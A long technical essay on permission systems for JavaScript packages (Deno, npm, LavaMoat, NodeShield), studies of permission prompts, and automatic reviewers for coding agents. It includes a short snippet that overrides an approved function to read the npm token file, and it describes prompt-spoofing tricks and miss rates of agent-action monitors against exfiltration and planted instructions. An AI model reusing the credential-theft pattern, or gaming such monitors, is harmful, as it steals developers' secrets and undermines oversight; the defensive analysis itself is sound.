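AlHamdan and Staicu studied 5,400 packages from deno.land, then Deno's main registry, as they stood in November 2022. They searched each package's README for permission flags. Of the 1,123 packages that documented permissions, only 53 used fine-grained ones such as `--allow-write="./log.txt"`. Another 33 had instructions to allow everything.

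AlHamdan and Staicu blame the long lists of flags, a problem that permission sets have since reduced. But a library's author often can't be more specific. The README of a general HTTP client can only recommend `--allow-net`, because the author doesn't know which hosts a user's program will contact. The count therefore shows what authors recommend, but users may grant less.

The researchers also searched the packages' code for calls that need permissions. They found network calls in the code of 237 packages, but in the dependencies of 2,714, half of the total. The search counted calls even if the program never reaches them, so fewer than half of the packages may use the network. For each of six of Deno's eight permissions, between 2,713 and 2,743 packages contain relevant calls when dependencies are included, although between 177 and 1,491 contain them in their own code. The most likely explanation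 is that most of these packages share a dependency that contains all six kinds of call, perhaps Deno's standard library. A package that used this library only to join two file paths would then be counted as using the network.

The search probably also missed some calls. It covered 103 built-in functions and found network calls in the code of 237 packages, while 385 packages documented unrestricted network access. Part of the difference may come from packages that access the network through their dependencies. The README search seems more reliable, since a manual check of 50 packages found no errors.

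### Inheriting or hiding the needs of dependencies

In the system by Ferreira and colleagues, packages inherit the permissions their dependencies need, so `weather` and every package that imports it need the network permission. If the policy leaves out inherited permissions, only `http-client` has an entry for the network.

The Deno figures show how quickly inherited permissions become uninformative. Even if the count of 2,714 is far too high, a reviewer who saw "network" next to half of all packages would learn little from the label. An attacker who inserted code into a harmless package would also gain every permission the package had inherited.

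But hiding these needs can surprise users. AlHamdan and Staicu give the example of `open`, a package that opens web addresses in the user's browser. Its documentation lists no permissions, so a user might reasonably guess that it needs permission to start programs. With only that permission, it works on Windows but not on Linux, where one of its dependencies, `is_wsl`, also has to read a file. This requirement is in the documentation for `is_wsl` but not in the documentation for `open`.

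NodeShield doesn't give a package the permissions that only its dependencies need, but it includes them when it shows the policy to a reviewer. In one of Cornelissen and Balliu's tests, an attack used a security hole in `mobile-icon-resizer` that lets attackers run their own code, and tried to access files. NodeShield blocked it because the package doesn't need file access itself, although some of its dependencies do. If the package had inherited their permission, the attack would have worked.

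A list that combines a package's permissions with those of its dependencies is more useful to reviewers than a list of the package's own permissions. `ps-tree`, a package that lists a process's child processes, depended on `event-stream`, which attackers compromised in 2018. If the attackers hadn't disguised their code, the combined list would have shown that `ps-tree` now required network access and encryption, even though its own permissions hadn't changed.

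This split seems better than applying either rule throughout, but the reviewer has to catch confused deputy problems unless the policy also restricts which packages each package may import, as LavaMoat's does.

### Permissions for single functions

Functions in the same package often need very different permissions. `cliffy`, a Deno package for building command-line programs, has a function that asks the user a question and suggests answers. It normally needs no permissions, but with the option `files: true` it suggests file names and has to read folders. If the developer gives `cliffy` read access for one such question, every other function in the package gets it too. Giving read access to that function alone would still be too broad, because the function needs it only when called with `files: true`. To match the need exactly, permissions would have to be set for each call.

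Finer rules can stop some attacks that coarser ones miss. Cornelissen and Balliu ran 24 attacks on packages that accidentally let outsiders run code. NodeShield detected 21, and the other three used permissions that the packages legitimately had. Ohm and colleagues' tool, which controls individual global variables and functions, stopped two of those three. It stopped only 12 of the 24, partly because eight attacks involved packages that didn't work with it, though its finer rules may not have caused that problem. Cornelissen and Balliu also found its policies too long.

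Teliva, an environment for small apps that come with their source code, once let users grant permissions to single functions, but the feature was dropped. Apps started with no access to files or the network. A user could read one function and grant broad permissions to it alone, without reading the rest of the app. This suited a file browser, which needs to open files all over the computer. Its author could put the code that opens files into one function, and the user could check that the function opened a single file or folder each time someone pressed Enter.

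In March 2022, the developer's Freewheeling Apps Devlog (2022) reported a serious flaw. An app could override functions, so the permission could end up with malicious code that the user had never read. In JavaScript, a similar trick could look like this:

```js
function openSelected(path) {      // the user reads and approves this
  return readFile(path);
}

// a thousand lines later:
openSelected = () => readFile("/home/ana/.npmrc");   // the npm token
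```

If the policy refers to the function by name, the second version inherits the first version's approval. Storing a fingerprint of the approved code would detect this replacement, but the app could instead replace `readFile` or another function that `openSelected` calls. Teliva went back to narrow permissions for the whole app, which left the developer looking for another way to check the file browser. Passing a capability with each call avoids the problem with names because the permission belongs to the object the caller passes.

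Permissions for single functions have a more basic weakness against supply chain attacks. Attackers who can publish a new version of `http-client` can change any of its functions, so they can put the malicious code in the one that has network access. Functions in a package also usually share variables. Rules for functions inside a package therefore help mainly against accidental security holes, as in Cornelissen and Balliu's 24 tests. A limit on a call is different because it is set by the server, whose code the attacker doesn't control.

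For most programs, it makes sense to set permissions per package, start each package with none, and grant the few that need access only specific files and hosts. Developers can then limit individual calls where a package handles something especially valuable.

### Deno's prototype for single APIs

An API is a set of functions that a runtime or library offers to other code. Deno's prototype from July 2026 gives each network function its own permission, for example `fetch`, `Deno.connect` or `WebSocket`. A developer could run a script like this:

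```
DENO_ALLOW_API="fetch('*.example.com')" deno run --allow-net client.ts
```

The script could now use only `fetch`, and only for subdomains of `example.com`, even though `--allow-net` permits any connection. The change to Deno is small. According to the commit message by Deno's developers, every permission check already receives the name of the function, which Deno otherwise uses only in prompts and error messages. If the developer has provided a list, the prototype compares this name with it before applying the usual rules; otherwise, Deno behaves as before.

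Deno already divides permissions this way for information about the machine. For instance, `--allow-sys="osRelease"` lets a program find out the operating system's version but not how much memory the machine has. This works because each function reveals something different. Network functions overlap much more. If `Deno.connect` is blocked, `colour` can still send the token with `fetch`, provided the destination is on the list. Separate permissions for contacting other machines and for waiting for incoming connections would be more useful.

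The prototype covers only the network and applies to the whole program. Deno's permission reference still didn't mention the prototype in late November 2026, and an official release looks as unlikely as one for `--deny-module`.

### Four difficult cases

A permission rule that covers a whole category, a package or the function `fetch` won't stop a compromised HTTP client from sending data out. A list of allowed hosts will, unless the attacker can receive data through one of them, for example by opening an account with a public file-storage service on the list. Some programs, such as a search engine that follows links, can't list their hosts in advance. They can still give the client a connection to only one host per call, and the policy can deny the client access to files and environment variables so that it has fewer secrets to send.

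A plugin loader imports packages that its author may never have heard of. If the loader must hold the permissions of everything it imports, it needs every permission that any plugin might require. Stack inspection causes the same problem, because the loader is on the stack when it starts a plugin. It is better to leave the plugins' permissions out of the loader's entry, give each plugin its own entry and let the loader import only the plugins on a list. A new plugin then fails until someone adds it to the list. Cornelissen and Balliu's tests with harmless programs suggest that such failures would be common, since all 18 false alarms concerned imports rather than the seven permissions. In Deno, a loader that computes file names at run time may also need permission to read those files, and every other package on the thread then gets that permission too.

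Suppose `logger` adds a function, `ship`, that sends each line to a log service. `ship` needs the network permission, which would let a compromised `logger` send everything it receives to any machine. A rule that allows connections only to the log service blocks other destinations. Separate permissions for `info` and `ship` add almost no protection, because `info` can save a visitor's password in a variable for `ship` to send. Moving `ship` to another package doesn't help much either, since that package has to receive the lines. The server can protect the password only by removing it before calling `logger`.

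The hardest case involves two permissions that look harmless separately. One package, `settings`, reads configuration files but has no network access. Another, `stats`, reports visitor numbers to an outside service but can't read files. If an attacker controls both, `settings` can put the database password in a shared object and `stats` can send it, without either operation violating the policy. With 12 packages that can read files and 8 others that can use the network, there are 96 such pairs. Dividing the packages into functions only adds more. Permissions that name specific files and hosts help, because they limit what the first package can read and where the second can send it.

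Separating permissions in time helps only if the order is right. Homebrew downloads first and then installs offline, so the network is closed when the installation code runs. If the server read its settings first and opened the network later, `settings` could keep the password in memory and send it once the network was open.

Permissions can also combine to have effects that aren't obvious from their names, as when AlHamdan and Staicu used import statements to send data without network permission. OSV's *CVE-2026-49983* (2026) reports that before Deno 2.8.1, a program with permission to read a settings file could load the file's contents into the environment variables, even if the developer had denied access to those variables. Reviewing the two rules separately would not have revealed the problem.

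## Writing, reviewing and updating permissions

The policies that Cornelissen and Balliu generated for NodeShield contained 64 permissions on average. Somebody has to produce such a policy, check it, and keep it correct as the packages change. Suppose the web server doesn't use `colour` yet, and its developer runs `npm install colour`.

### Installing a package without running it

Until npm version 12 arrived in July 2026, that command also ran the install scripts of `colour` and all its dependencies. GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026) confirms that version 12 is now the standard release. By default, it doesn't run dependencies' install scripts, and it refuses dependencies that come from a Git repository or a web address instead of the registry.

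The block on scripts also covers packages that contain a file called `binding.gyp`. npm used to compile their native code automatically, even without an install script. NodeSource's *Blocking Install Scripts Is Not a Silver Bullet* (2026) reports that attackers were exploiting this by June, in about 57 packages. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) explains that the rule on Git closes another route. A Git dependency could include a settings file that replaced the Git program, which let it run code even if the developer had turned install scripts off.

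Some packages need their scripts, mostly to compile or download native code, and `thumbnail` is probably one of them. npm skips the script and lists the package at the end of the installation. If the developer then runs `npm install-scripts approve thumbnail`, npm adds an entry to the project's `package.json`:

```json
"allowScripts": {
  "thumbnail@2.1.0": true
}
```

The approved script runs with all the developer's rights, so approval controls whether it runs but not what it does. The approval covers only version 2.1.0, so npm skips the script in 2.1.1 until someone approves it again. ApostropheCMS's *npm v12 install scripts* calls this default a trap for long-lived projects and recommends approving most packages by name alone. Such an approval also applies to later versions, including any that an attacker publishes. npm also offers `approve --all`, which approves every pending script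 at once, except those of packages the developer has explicitly denied.

The new default closes an important route for attacks, since almost every worm and credential stealer on npm since late 2025 ran during installation, according to Socket (2026). Other package managers had changed their defaults earlier. For example, pnpm stopped running dependencies' scripts in January 2025, and since April 2026 it has held back new releases for 24 hours by default (Robert, 2026).

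But npm v12 doesn't block code that runs when the server imports a package. The AsyncAPI attack, which used only such code, came a week after the release, and Microsoft's *Unpacking AsyncAPI npm supply chain compromise* (2026) describes the absence of install scripts as deliberate. The `keyv` attack in August still used an install script (Raj, *npm malware compromises keyv and cacheable with 500m weekly downloads*, 2026), presumably because many machines still had older versions of npm. Expert Insights' *Supply Chain Attackers Are Targeting AI Coding Tools* (2026) reports that attackers are also trying tasks that code editors run automatically.

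NodeSource recommends the Node.js permission model for code that has already loaded. The model applies to the whole process and doesn't restrict environment variables, so `colour` could read a password from one and send it to any machine the server is allowed to contact.

GitHub also plans to make stolen publishing tokens less useful. From about January 2027, tokens that bypass two-factor authentication will only be able to prepare a release, which a person must then approve. This would hamper worms that spread with such tokens, but the AsyncAPI attacker and the first wave of the `keyv` attack used the projects' own automated release processes instead.

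### Asking the author

After the installation, `colour` is on the disk and none of its code has run. This is the best time to write its policy.

The `colour` package's author could write its list of permissions, and would know about rarely used features that a scan or a test might miss. In the system that Ferreira and colleagues designed, authors declare permissions in a file inside the package, the npm website shows them, and users accept them at installation. If an update adds permissions, the package manager doesn't install it until the user confirms.

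Package authors may also request more permissions than they need, as Android developers are known to do. Ferreira and colleagues expect this to be less common on npm, because few authors there want extra access for advertising and the users are developers who can judge whether a request makes sense.

Whoever can publish a package also controls its declaration. The AsyncAPI attacker could push changes to the source code and could have changed a declaration too. Users would then be protected only if they noticed the change and refused it.

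### Inferring a policy from the code

A tool can generate the policy instead. The command `lavamoat app.js --autopolicy` finds which modules, global objects and other packages each of the server's dependencies uses, and writes the result to `policy.json`. The policy doesn't restrict the server's own code. The analysis is safe even if a package is malicious, because it reads the code without running it.

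Choosing permissions by searching a library's code can grant too much or too little. NodeShield's prototype searches for imports and for the words `fetch`, `eval` and `process`. If `colour` contained the error message "could not process this text", NodeShield would give it the `system` permission, which includes access to environment variables. A search also misses imports whose names the code computes as it runs. Ferreira and colleagues found computed imports in 8% of npm packages, though these rarely seemed to involve sensitive modules.

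LavaMoat's analysis is more precise, since it can often list the individual functions a package uses. Sometimes it can't tell and grants a whole object. For example, a package that only reads `process.env`, where the environment variables are, may get all of `process`, which can also load modules and start other programs. LavaMoat's *Using Policies* tells developers to leave the generated file alone and put corrections in a second one, `policy-override.json`:

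```json
"globals": {
  "process": false,
  "process.env": true
}
```

The opposite correction fails without warning. If a developer allows `process` and denies `process.env`, packages can still read `process.env`, because the first line already grants the whole object.

Inference also grants access for features that the server never uses, and the ZTD-Java tests suggest that there are many of them.

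### Recording what a package does

Recording a run avoids these unnecessary grants. If the developer sets `DENO_AUDIT_PERMISSIONS` to a file path, Deno writes every permission check to that file, whether it allowed the access or not. With invented values, two lines of the log could look like this:

```json
{"v":1,"datetime":"2026-12-01T09:14:18Z","permission":"write","value":"./logs/server.log"}
{"v":1,"datetime":"2026-12-01T09:14:26Z","permission":"read","value":"/home/ana/.npmrc"}
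```

The second line should alarm the developer, because that file holds the npm token. The line doesn't show which package was responsible, so the developer also sets `DENO_TRACE_PERMISSIONS=1`, which makes Deno add the chain of function calls that led to each access. Here the chain would include a file from `colour`. Deno can't turn the result into a rule for `colour` alone, but the developer can use it to tighten the server's flags, move a package to a worker, or write a policy for another tool.

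Recording is riskier than inference because the code has to run. A developer who uses `-A` so that nothing interrupts the recording also lets a malicious package steal the token. NodeShield's log mode has the same problem, since it records violations without preventing them. A developer can instead start with an empty policy in exit mode, where NodeShield stops the program at the first violation. The developer adds the missing permission if it seems justified, restarts the program, and repeats this until it runs. This is tedious, and NodeShield's prototype doesn't fill in the policy automatically.

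A recording also leaves out anything the program didn't do during the recorded run. Cornelissen and Balliu tested harmless programs, sending each server a single request, and some runs covered as little as 3% of a program's lines. Real tests should cover more, but they often skip error handling and jobs that run once a year.

### If the first version is already malicious

If the developer first installs `colour` during the two hours when the attacker's version is available, any declaration comes from the attacker, and an inferred or recorded policy permits whatever the malicious code does.

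LavaMoat's *Reviewing Policy* therefore warns that a first policy provides no security until someone reviews it. The review is easy for `colour` but much harder for `http-client`, where only the exact hosts and files would look odd. Generating the policy from a version that is several months old helps if the package was hijacked recently, but not if it was malicious from the start.

For most projects, the best approach is to infer the policy from the code, remove any permissions that seem unnecessary, and run the tests with the policy enforced. NodeShield's exit mode is useful for these tests because a package can't hide a violation by catching the error. The developer then commits the policy file with the source code, so colleagues and build servers use the same rules and any later change is visible.

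### An update to `colour`

The harmless version of `colour` has an empty entry, which grants nothing, just like a missing one. Months later, the attacker publishes an update. The developer installs it and regenerates the policy, and the reviewer sees this change:

```diff
 "resources": {
-  "colour": {},
+  "colour": {
+    "builtin": {
+      "fs.readFileSync": true,
+      "https.request": true
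+    }
+  },
   "logger": {
     "builtin": { "fs.appendFile": true }
   }
 }
```

The reviewer can become suspicious without reading the new code. LavaMoat's guide uses almost the same example, a package for basic text operations that suddenly makes web requests and reads `process`. It suggests taking a closer look or denying the new access in the override file. Here, going back to the previous version would be safer, because code that tries to read the npm token may do other harm.

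If the attacker hides the imports, for instance by encrypting the code, the generator misses them and the policy doesn't change. The code then fails when it runs, as `flatmap-stream` did under NodeShield. The attacker therefore has to request the new permissions visibly or have the code blocked. Attackers don't face this choice with packages like `node-ipc`, which already had the permissions the attack needed.

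Other changes are harder to read. An update might let `colour` import `http-client` but no built-in modules, so the reviewer has to look up what `http-client` can do. LavaMoat also names each package by the shortest route to it through the dependency tree. Adding an unrelated package can shorten that route and change `server-kit>parser>colour` to `theme>colour`, even though the code is the same. But the new name could also belong to a different package called `colour`. The reviewer can compare the permissions under the two names, and should investigate if they are very different.

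### How much there is to review

Cornelissen and Balliu estimated the workload from the history of six open-source server projects. They went through up to 1,000 recent commits (saved changes to the code) in each and counted new permissions in those that changed dependencies. The number of such commits in this table follows from their totals and averages:

| Project | Commits that changed dependencies | Permissions of new dependencies | Permissions added by updates |
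|---|---|---|---|
| `connect` | 24 | 32 | 1 |
| `express` | 3 | 1 | 1 |
| `fastify` | 9 | 12 | 0 |
| `json-server` | 15 | 118 | 10 |
| `koa` | 63 | 800 | 7 |
| `st` | 10 | 20 | 5 |

Updates added 24 permissions in 124 commits, or about one for every five commits. Project averages ranged from 0 to 0.67 permissions per commit, or from 0.67 to 12.81 with new dependencies included. Nearly all the work therefore comes from adding packages, and a team can reduce it by adding fewer packages.

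Ferreira and colleagues replayed every 2018 update to the 100 most depended-upon npm packages and their dependencies. Of 5,042 updates, only 27 (0.5%) needed more permissions than the version before. Another 2,644 (52%) were to packages that needed no permissions before or after. The researchers suggest that developers could install these without review and concentrate on the 27.

The saving was much smaller for complete applications. In their sample of 20 command-line programs, only 6% of updates were to packages without permissions, while 86% were to packages with `all`. An update can't add permissions to a package that already has `all`, so the low number of requests partly reflects how coarse the permissions are. New requests were far more common with Ohm and colleagues' more detailed policies. Skipping reviews also has a risk, since a package without permissions can still return false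 results.

Both workload studies counted changes in old code, but they didn't measure how long a review takes or how often reviewers would recognise an attack. Ferreira and colleagues acknowledge that real developers may become complacent, or feel safer than they are because a permission system exists.

### A refusal on the live server

Suppose `logger` renames its file when it reaches 100 megabytes. The tests never write that much, so a recorded policy that lists individual functions allows `fs.appendFile` but not `fs.rename`. When the file reaches that size weeks later on the live server, the rename is refused.

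In NodeShield's exit mode, the attempt to rename the log file would stop the whole server. In throw mode, `logger` would get an error, and might catch it and keep writing to the same file. Log mode would allow the renaming, but it would also allow a theft. Throw mode seems best for most live servers, provided that refusals also trigger an alert, because a malicious package can catch the error too.

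The developer then has to find out whether the policy is incomplete or the package is malicious. A refusal just after an update is more suspicious than one in a version that has worked for months, but an older version can still be malicious, as `ordered-btree` did nothing until a program used a particular key. The safest response is to read the code that made the call and, if it is legitimate, add only `fs.rename` to the override file. Regenerating the whole policy is quicker, but it would also approve any other access the tool now finds.

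### Who does the work

In *chore: add the new policy.json review process documentation and config*, MetaMask, the wallet maker behind LavaMoat, has drafted a procedure that divides this work. An automatic check fails when a change in dependencies requires a new policy. The developer asks a bot to generate the policy and must then comment on it, including why any package needs powerful access such as starting programs. Developers who don't understand the change must say so. A security reviewer compares the comment with the policy and passes doubtful cases to specialists, who examine the package itself. Starting with the developer makes sense because, as the draft points out, developers know more than the reviewers about what the package is for, even though they know less about security.

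A wallet company can afford several reviewers, but in a small project the same person adds the package, writes the policy and approves it, usually while trying to finish something else. A missing permission stops that work immediately, whereas granting every permission fixes the error and has no visible drawback until an attack. Even then, the stolen passwords may belong to someone other than the developer who saved the time. This helps explain why Java developers granted `AllPermission`, and why `approve --all` is tempting.

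Tools can make broad permissions less convenient to grant. npm approves single versions by default, and LavaMoat marks permission to change a global object with `"write"` instead of `true`, so that it stands out in a review. In its *secure coding guidelines*, MetaMask asks developers to investigate each warning about dependencies and leave a short explanation, rather than dismiss all warnings with one command. Such rules help only if there are few warnings.

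AI models might take over some of the work, but there is little evidence of how well they would do it. None of the studies above tested how well models write or review package policies. MetaMask's draft mentions future tools for summarising policy changes, but doesn't specify whether they would use AI. A model could read an update and point to the line that needs `https`, so the reviewer wouldn't have to search for it. However, an attacker could add comments to the code to mislead the model. Models also make mistakes without such interference, as Claude Code did when it first took the LiteLLM malware for a fault in its own tools.

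A coding agent asked to fix a failing build may also grant whatever permissions make the error disappear. A model could reasonably be allowed to remove permissions without asking, because a wrong removal usually causes an error that someone notices, but a person should approve every permission it adds.

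## When to ask for permission, and whom

A person should approve each new permission, but how good the decision is depends on who that person is and what they are doing when the question arrives. Suppose the attacker's update of `colour` tries to read the file that holds the npm token. A permission system can respond in four ways:

| Response | What helps the decision | What is missing |
|---|---|---|
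| Ask the developer at installation or update | The developer knows what the package is for | Often the time to find out what the new code does |
| Ask the program's user at run time | The user knows what they were just doing | Any idea which packages the program contains |
| Refuse silently | Nobody has to decide | A way to tell an attack from a forgotten permission |
| Follow a written policy | A reviewer could think about it in advance | Needs that nobody foresaw |

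If the web server asked for permission at run time, nobody suitable would be there to answer. Visitors use the server from other machines and shouldn't make decisions about the developer's files, and the developer isn't watching the terminal.

A desktop program does have someone at the screen. Suppose a photo organiser uses `thumbnail`, and its user sees the question "Allow `thumbnail` to start another program?" The user chose the photo organiser but has never heard of `thumbnail`. The question would look the same whether the other program was an image converter or a credential stealer. Refusing might stop the pictures from appearing, so most people would probably allow it.

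Silently denying permission requests saves users from having to answer them but can break programs. *Android Permissions Remystified* (Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues, 2015) mentions AppFence, a system that let phone users withhold data from apps or substitute fake data. AppFence broke features in a third of the apps tested.

### Permission lists at installation

Before version 6, Android listed an app's permissions just before installation, and the user could accept them all or cancel. In *Android Permissions*, Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012) tested whether people used this list. They surveyed 308 Android users online and watched 25 others install apps on their own phones, without revealing at first that the study was about security.

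In the survey, 17.5% of respondents said they had looked at the permissions the last time they installed an app. The researchers also watched people and assessed whether 24 of them paid attention to the permission list. Four looked at it, ten knew about it but ignored it, and ten had never noticed it.

Few people understood the permissions either. Only 8 of 302 survey participants correctly answered all three multiple-choice questions about what permissions allow. An answer counted as correct only if it included every correct option and no wrong ones, though about half of the answers contained at least one correct option. The design of the list also caused mistakes. Android put the permission to place phone calls under the large heading "Services that cost you money", and 27 people thought it allowed credit card purchases, while 30 thought it allowed calls.

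Still, a fifth of the people in the laboratory study could describe a time they cancelled an installation because of permissions. Felt and colleagues suggest that this minority could protect others by writing about permissions in app reviews. The idea might work even better for packages, because one developer who notices that `colour` requests network access can report it, and npm can remove the release for everyone.

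### Requests that surprised users

To study what apps did after installation, Wijesekera and colleagues gave 36 people phones with a modified version of Android that logged every access to protected data and functions for a week. When an app used one of 12 sensitive permissions, the phone sometimes took a screenshot. Afterwards, the participants looked at their screenshots, learned what the app had accessed, and said whether they would have blocked that access.

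The phones logged 27 million requests, or more than 100,000 per person per day. For three quarters of the requests, nothing on the phone showed that the app was running, usually because the screen was off. Thirty of the 36 participants would have blocked at least one of the requests they saw, and together they would have blocked 35% of the 423 requests. Their most common reason was that the app didn't seem to need the data. They objected to 43% of requests from apps that weren't visible, compared with 29% of requests from visible apps.

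Nobody could have answered every request, because apps used the 12 sensitive permissions about every 20 seconds. Asking once for each combination of app and permission didn't work well either, because a person's first answer matched their later ones only 51% of the time. The match rose to 84% when requests were also separated by whether the app was visible. Asking once for each combination of app, permission and visibility would have meant an average of 34 prompts in the first week, or 29 if the phone asked only when an app was about to get sensitive data.

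For a library, the nearest equivalent of visibility is probably the chain of calls that led to the request. A developer might want `http-client` to open a connection when the server fetches a page, but not while the package is loading.

### Prompts at first use

iOS and newer versions of Android ask when an app first needs a sensitive permission. Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues (2017), in *The Feasibility of Dynamically Granted Permissions*, studied this approach with 131 people over an average of 32 days. About once a day, the phone asked whether they would have allowed an access that had just happened. They wanted to block 60% of these requests. A system that asked at first use and then kept to the answer would have matched their wishes 84% of the time, compared with 25% for permissions granted at installation.

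The researchers also trained a model to predict people's answers from their earlier decisions, the app on the screen, and habits such as how they locked their phones. Its predictions were right 96.8% of the time, and the user would see a prompt only when the model's confidence was low.

People refuse far less often when refusing has consequences. *A Large Scale Study of User Behavior, Expectations and Engagement* (Cao, Xia and colleagues, 2021) followed 1,719 people in ten countries and regions for 30 days as they used their own phones. The participants denied 16.7% of about 36,000 requests. A refusal could disable a feature, whereas the answers in the 2017 study changed nothing. The 2017 study also asked about background access, which people tend to dislike more.

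In real decisions, people also denied unexpected requests more often (26.9%) than expected ones (12.2%). Their most common reasons for granting a permission were that they wanted a feature that needed it, thought the app wouldn't work without it, or trusted the developer. Someone using the photo organiser can hardly apply these reasons to `thumbnail`, because they don't know what it does in the program or who wrote it.

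It is unclear whether an app's explanation persuades people to grant a permission or only moves their refusal to an earlier screen. Cao and colleagues found that people denied 7.1% of requests that followed an explanation and 15.4% of the others. But the study counted only formal requests, and the app never made one if the person tapped "Not now" in the explanation. This happened 540 times, against 1,804 explanations that led to a formal decision. If these cases count as refusals, the denial rate with an explanation rises to about 28%. Even if explanations do persuade people, an attacker can write a plausible one.

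### Habituation

Habituation means people respond less and less to something that keeps happening without consequences. They read the first few permission prompts and later click "Allow" by reflex. In Felt and colleagues' laboratory study, three of the ten people who knew about the permission list but ignored it said they used to read it. One participant had stopped worrying about location access because so many of her apps requested it.

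Allowing a request without reading it is a reasonable response to most prompts. If one request in 1,000 is malicious, a person who allows everything is right 99.9% of the time and saves a lot of reading, but the one mistake can give away an npm token. Asking more often doesn't help, because every harmless prompt strengthens the habit of allowing requests unread.

Researchers can measure habituation more directly with coding agents, which may ask for permission dozens of times in one session. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through each session, the experiment replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. About 17% refused when it appeared early in a session, but only about 5% refused after 50 or more prompts.

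Some of this drop may reflect differences between people, because testers who approved everything quickly may have been more likely to reach 50 prompts. The testers were also risking less than they would on their own projects. But even the early figure is poor, so either the testers had already formed the habit of approving quickly in their normal work, or many people can't recognise a dangerous command even when they are fresh.

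### Prompts that don't name the package

Deno's prompts also don't always show which code triggered them. In *Is there any way to trace where permissions prompts are coming from?*, a 2022 post on Deno's help site, Fish described a prompt for read access to the current folder. The prompt named the function that needed access, `Deno.cwd()`, which tells a program which folder it is running in, but didn't identify the code that called it. Fish's own code checked for the permission before calling the function, so the likely source was an npm dependency. Another user suggested refusing the request to get an error message with the chain of calls, then realised that the responsible code might catch the error. A program's users would have even less chance than its developer of finding the source.

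Deno can now show the chain of calls with each prompt, but only if the developer turns on the slow tracing described earlier. Deno concedes that asking for the narrowest possible permission may annoy users. The quickest way to stop the prompts is to type `A` for "allow all", which gives every package on the thread that whole category of permission.

A program could also disguise the prompt. JuliaLang's *Deno is vulnerable to race condition via interactive permission prompt spoofing*, an entry in a vulnerability database, describes how a program with several threads could do this. While Deno waited for an answer, another thread could clear the screen and print "Do you want to continue?" A user who typed `y` would unknowingly grant access to a file. The trick depended on exact timing and didn't always work. Deno fixed the flaw in version 1.29.3, and Cybersecurity Help's *Improper Neutralization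 of Escape, Meta, or Control Sequences in Deno* (2023) dates the report to January 2023.

A later flaw involved control sequences, hidden characters that make a terminal do things such as change the text colour. Deno removed them from the path it displayed but not from the path it granted. JuliaLang's *Deno's `deno_runtime` vulnerable to interactive permission prompt spoofing via improper ANSI stripping* gives an example in which the user sees a request for `/tmp/hellotc/hosts`, but typing `y` gives access to `/etc/hosts`. Deno's published prompt code makes such characters visible and limits the length of a prompt. `colour` would have been a good place to hide this attack because it normally produces control sequences.

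### What a library prompt should show

A better prompt for the attack on the npm token might look like this:

```
colour 3.1.1 wants to read a file
  File:       /home/ana/.npmrc (holds your npm token)
  Called by:  server > colour
  Change:     version 3.1.0 did not read any files

  [n] Refuse   [o] Allow once   [p] Propose a policy change
```

The runtime must fill in every line itself, because `colour` could supply a false name or false reasons. It should follow any links before showing the path, and grant exactly the access it shows. The line about the previous version shows the developer that the request is unexpected, which made people more careful in the phone studies.

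Allowing an access once is useful because the developer may only want to finish a test. In Cao and colleagues' study, people would have preferred to grant the permission temporarily in 24% of the cases where they granted it. The last option starts the review described in the previous section instead of changing the policy immediately, so a tired developer can't grant permanent access by pressing a single key. There is no option to allow all files.

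The program must not be able to draw over the prompt or answer it. Deno's prompt shares a terminal with the program's output, which made the two-thread trick possible. A separate window would be safer, or the runtime could hold back all output until the user answers.

The best time to ask is during an installation, an update or a test run, because the developer has just chosen the package and can still go back to the old version. The tool should combine all the requests from one update into a single question. On the live server, it should follow the policy instead of asking.

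End users should be asked only about things they recognise, such as whether a photo organiser may open their pictures folder. The developer then decides which of the program's libraries get that access.

### How often people approve an agent's requests

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. By August 2026, Anthropic put the figure at 97%. A quarter of interactive sessions began with permission checks turned off, and almost half of the active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules covered every Python or Node.js command, which is practically the same as allowing everything.

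In *I don't want AI agents controlling my laptop*, Alpert (2025) describes why a developer might be tempted to turn off an agent's permission prompts. Alpert usually approves the specific commands an agent asks about, so turning the prompts off would change little. A more useful rule would give the agent access to everything except the password manager, the bank and stored keys, but Alpert sees no good way to express that on today's desktop systems.

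Most commands are harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. OpenAI's automatic reviewer approves an even larger share. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) gives an example based on OpenAI's own use of Codex, its coding agent. Of 10,000 actions, 9,280 needed no approval because they stayed inside the sandbox, which limits where Codex can write and blocks the network. The other 720 would each have interrupted a person, but a second model reviewed them instead, approving 713 and refusing seven. Codex found a safer way to continue in four of the seven cases and stopped to ask the user in three.

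The sandbox therefore handled 93% of the actions without a permission request, and the reviewer decided almost all of the rest. These numbers depend on the task and how much the sandbox allows.

### How well automatic approval works

Both companies have tested their reviewers on harmless and dangerous actions:

| Test | Company | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real actions by employees' agents | Anthropic | Blocked 0.4% of harmless actions |
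| 52 real actions that went beyond what the user wanted | Anthropic | Missed 17% |
| 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | Anthropic | Missed 5.7% |
| The dangerous commands from the experiment with testers | Anthropic | Missed 11%; people missed 86.4% |
| Artificial cases of agents overstepping their task | OpenAI | Missed 9.7% |
| Artificial attacks through planted instructions | OpenAI | Missed 0.7% |

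The 17% is only about nine actions, so the true rate could be quite different. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but misjudged what the user had agreed to. For example, it could take "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) as consent to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic admits that the system is arguably a step backwards for someone who checks every action carefully, though the experiment suggests that few people do.

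Results from normal use support the same conclusion, but less strongly. Anthropic looked at sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Among those with manual approval, 6.3% contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of those with automatic approval. But users had chosen the mode themselves, perhaps for different kinds of work. In an outside test, none of 720 attacks through planted instructions succeeded against three Claude models with automatic approval. This is weak evidence of the reviewer's effect, because Anthropic's latest models resisted nearly all the attacks without it.

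Anthropic made automatic approval the default for most individual and team plans in August 2026. Claude Code returns to asking the user after three refusals in a row or 20 in a session. OpenAI's testers misled its reviewer, which doesn't monitor what happens inside the sandbox. OpenAI's *Auto-review* notes that the user must still approve which apps on the computer Codex may operate.

An automatic reviewer for packages would have less information than Anthropic's reviewer, which compares each action with what the user asked for. Nobody gives a package like `colour` instructions in words, so a package reviewer could compare a request only with the package's description and earlier versions, and an attacker can rewrite the description.

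### Predicting what users would answer

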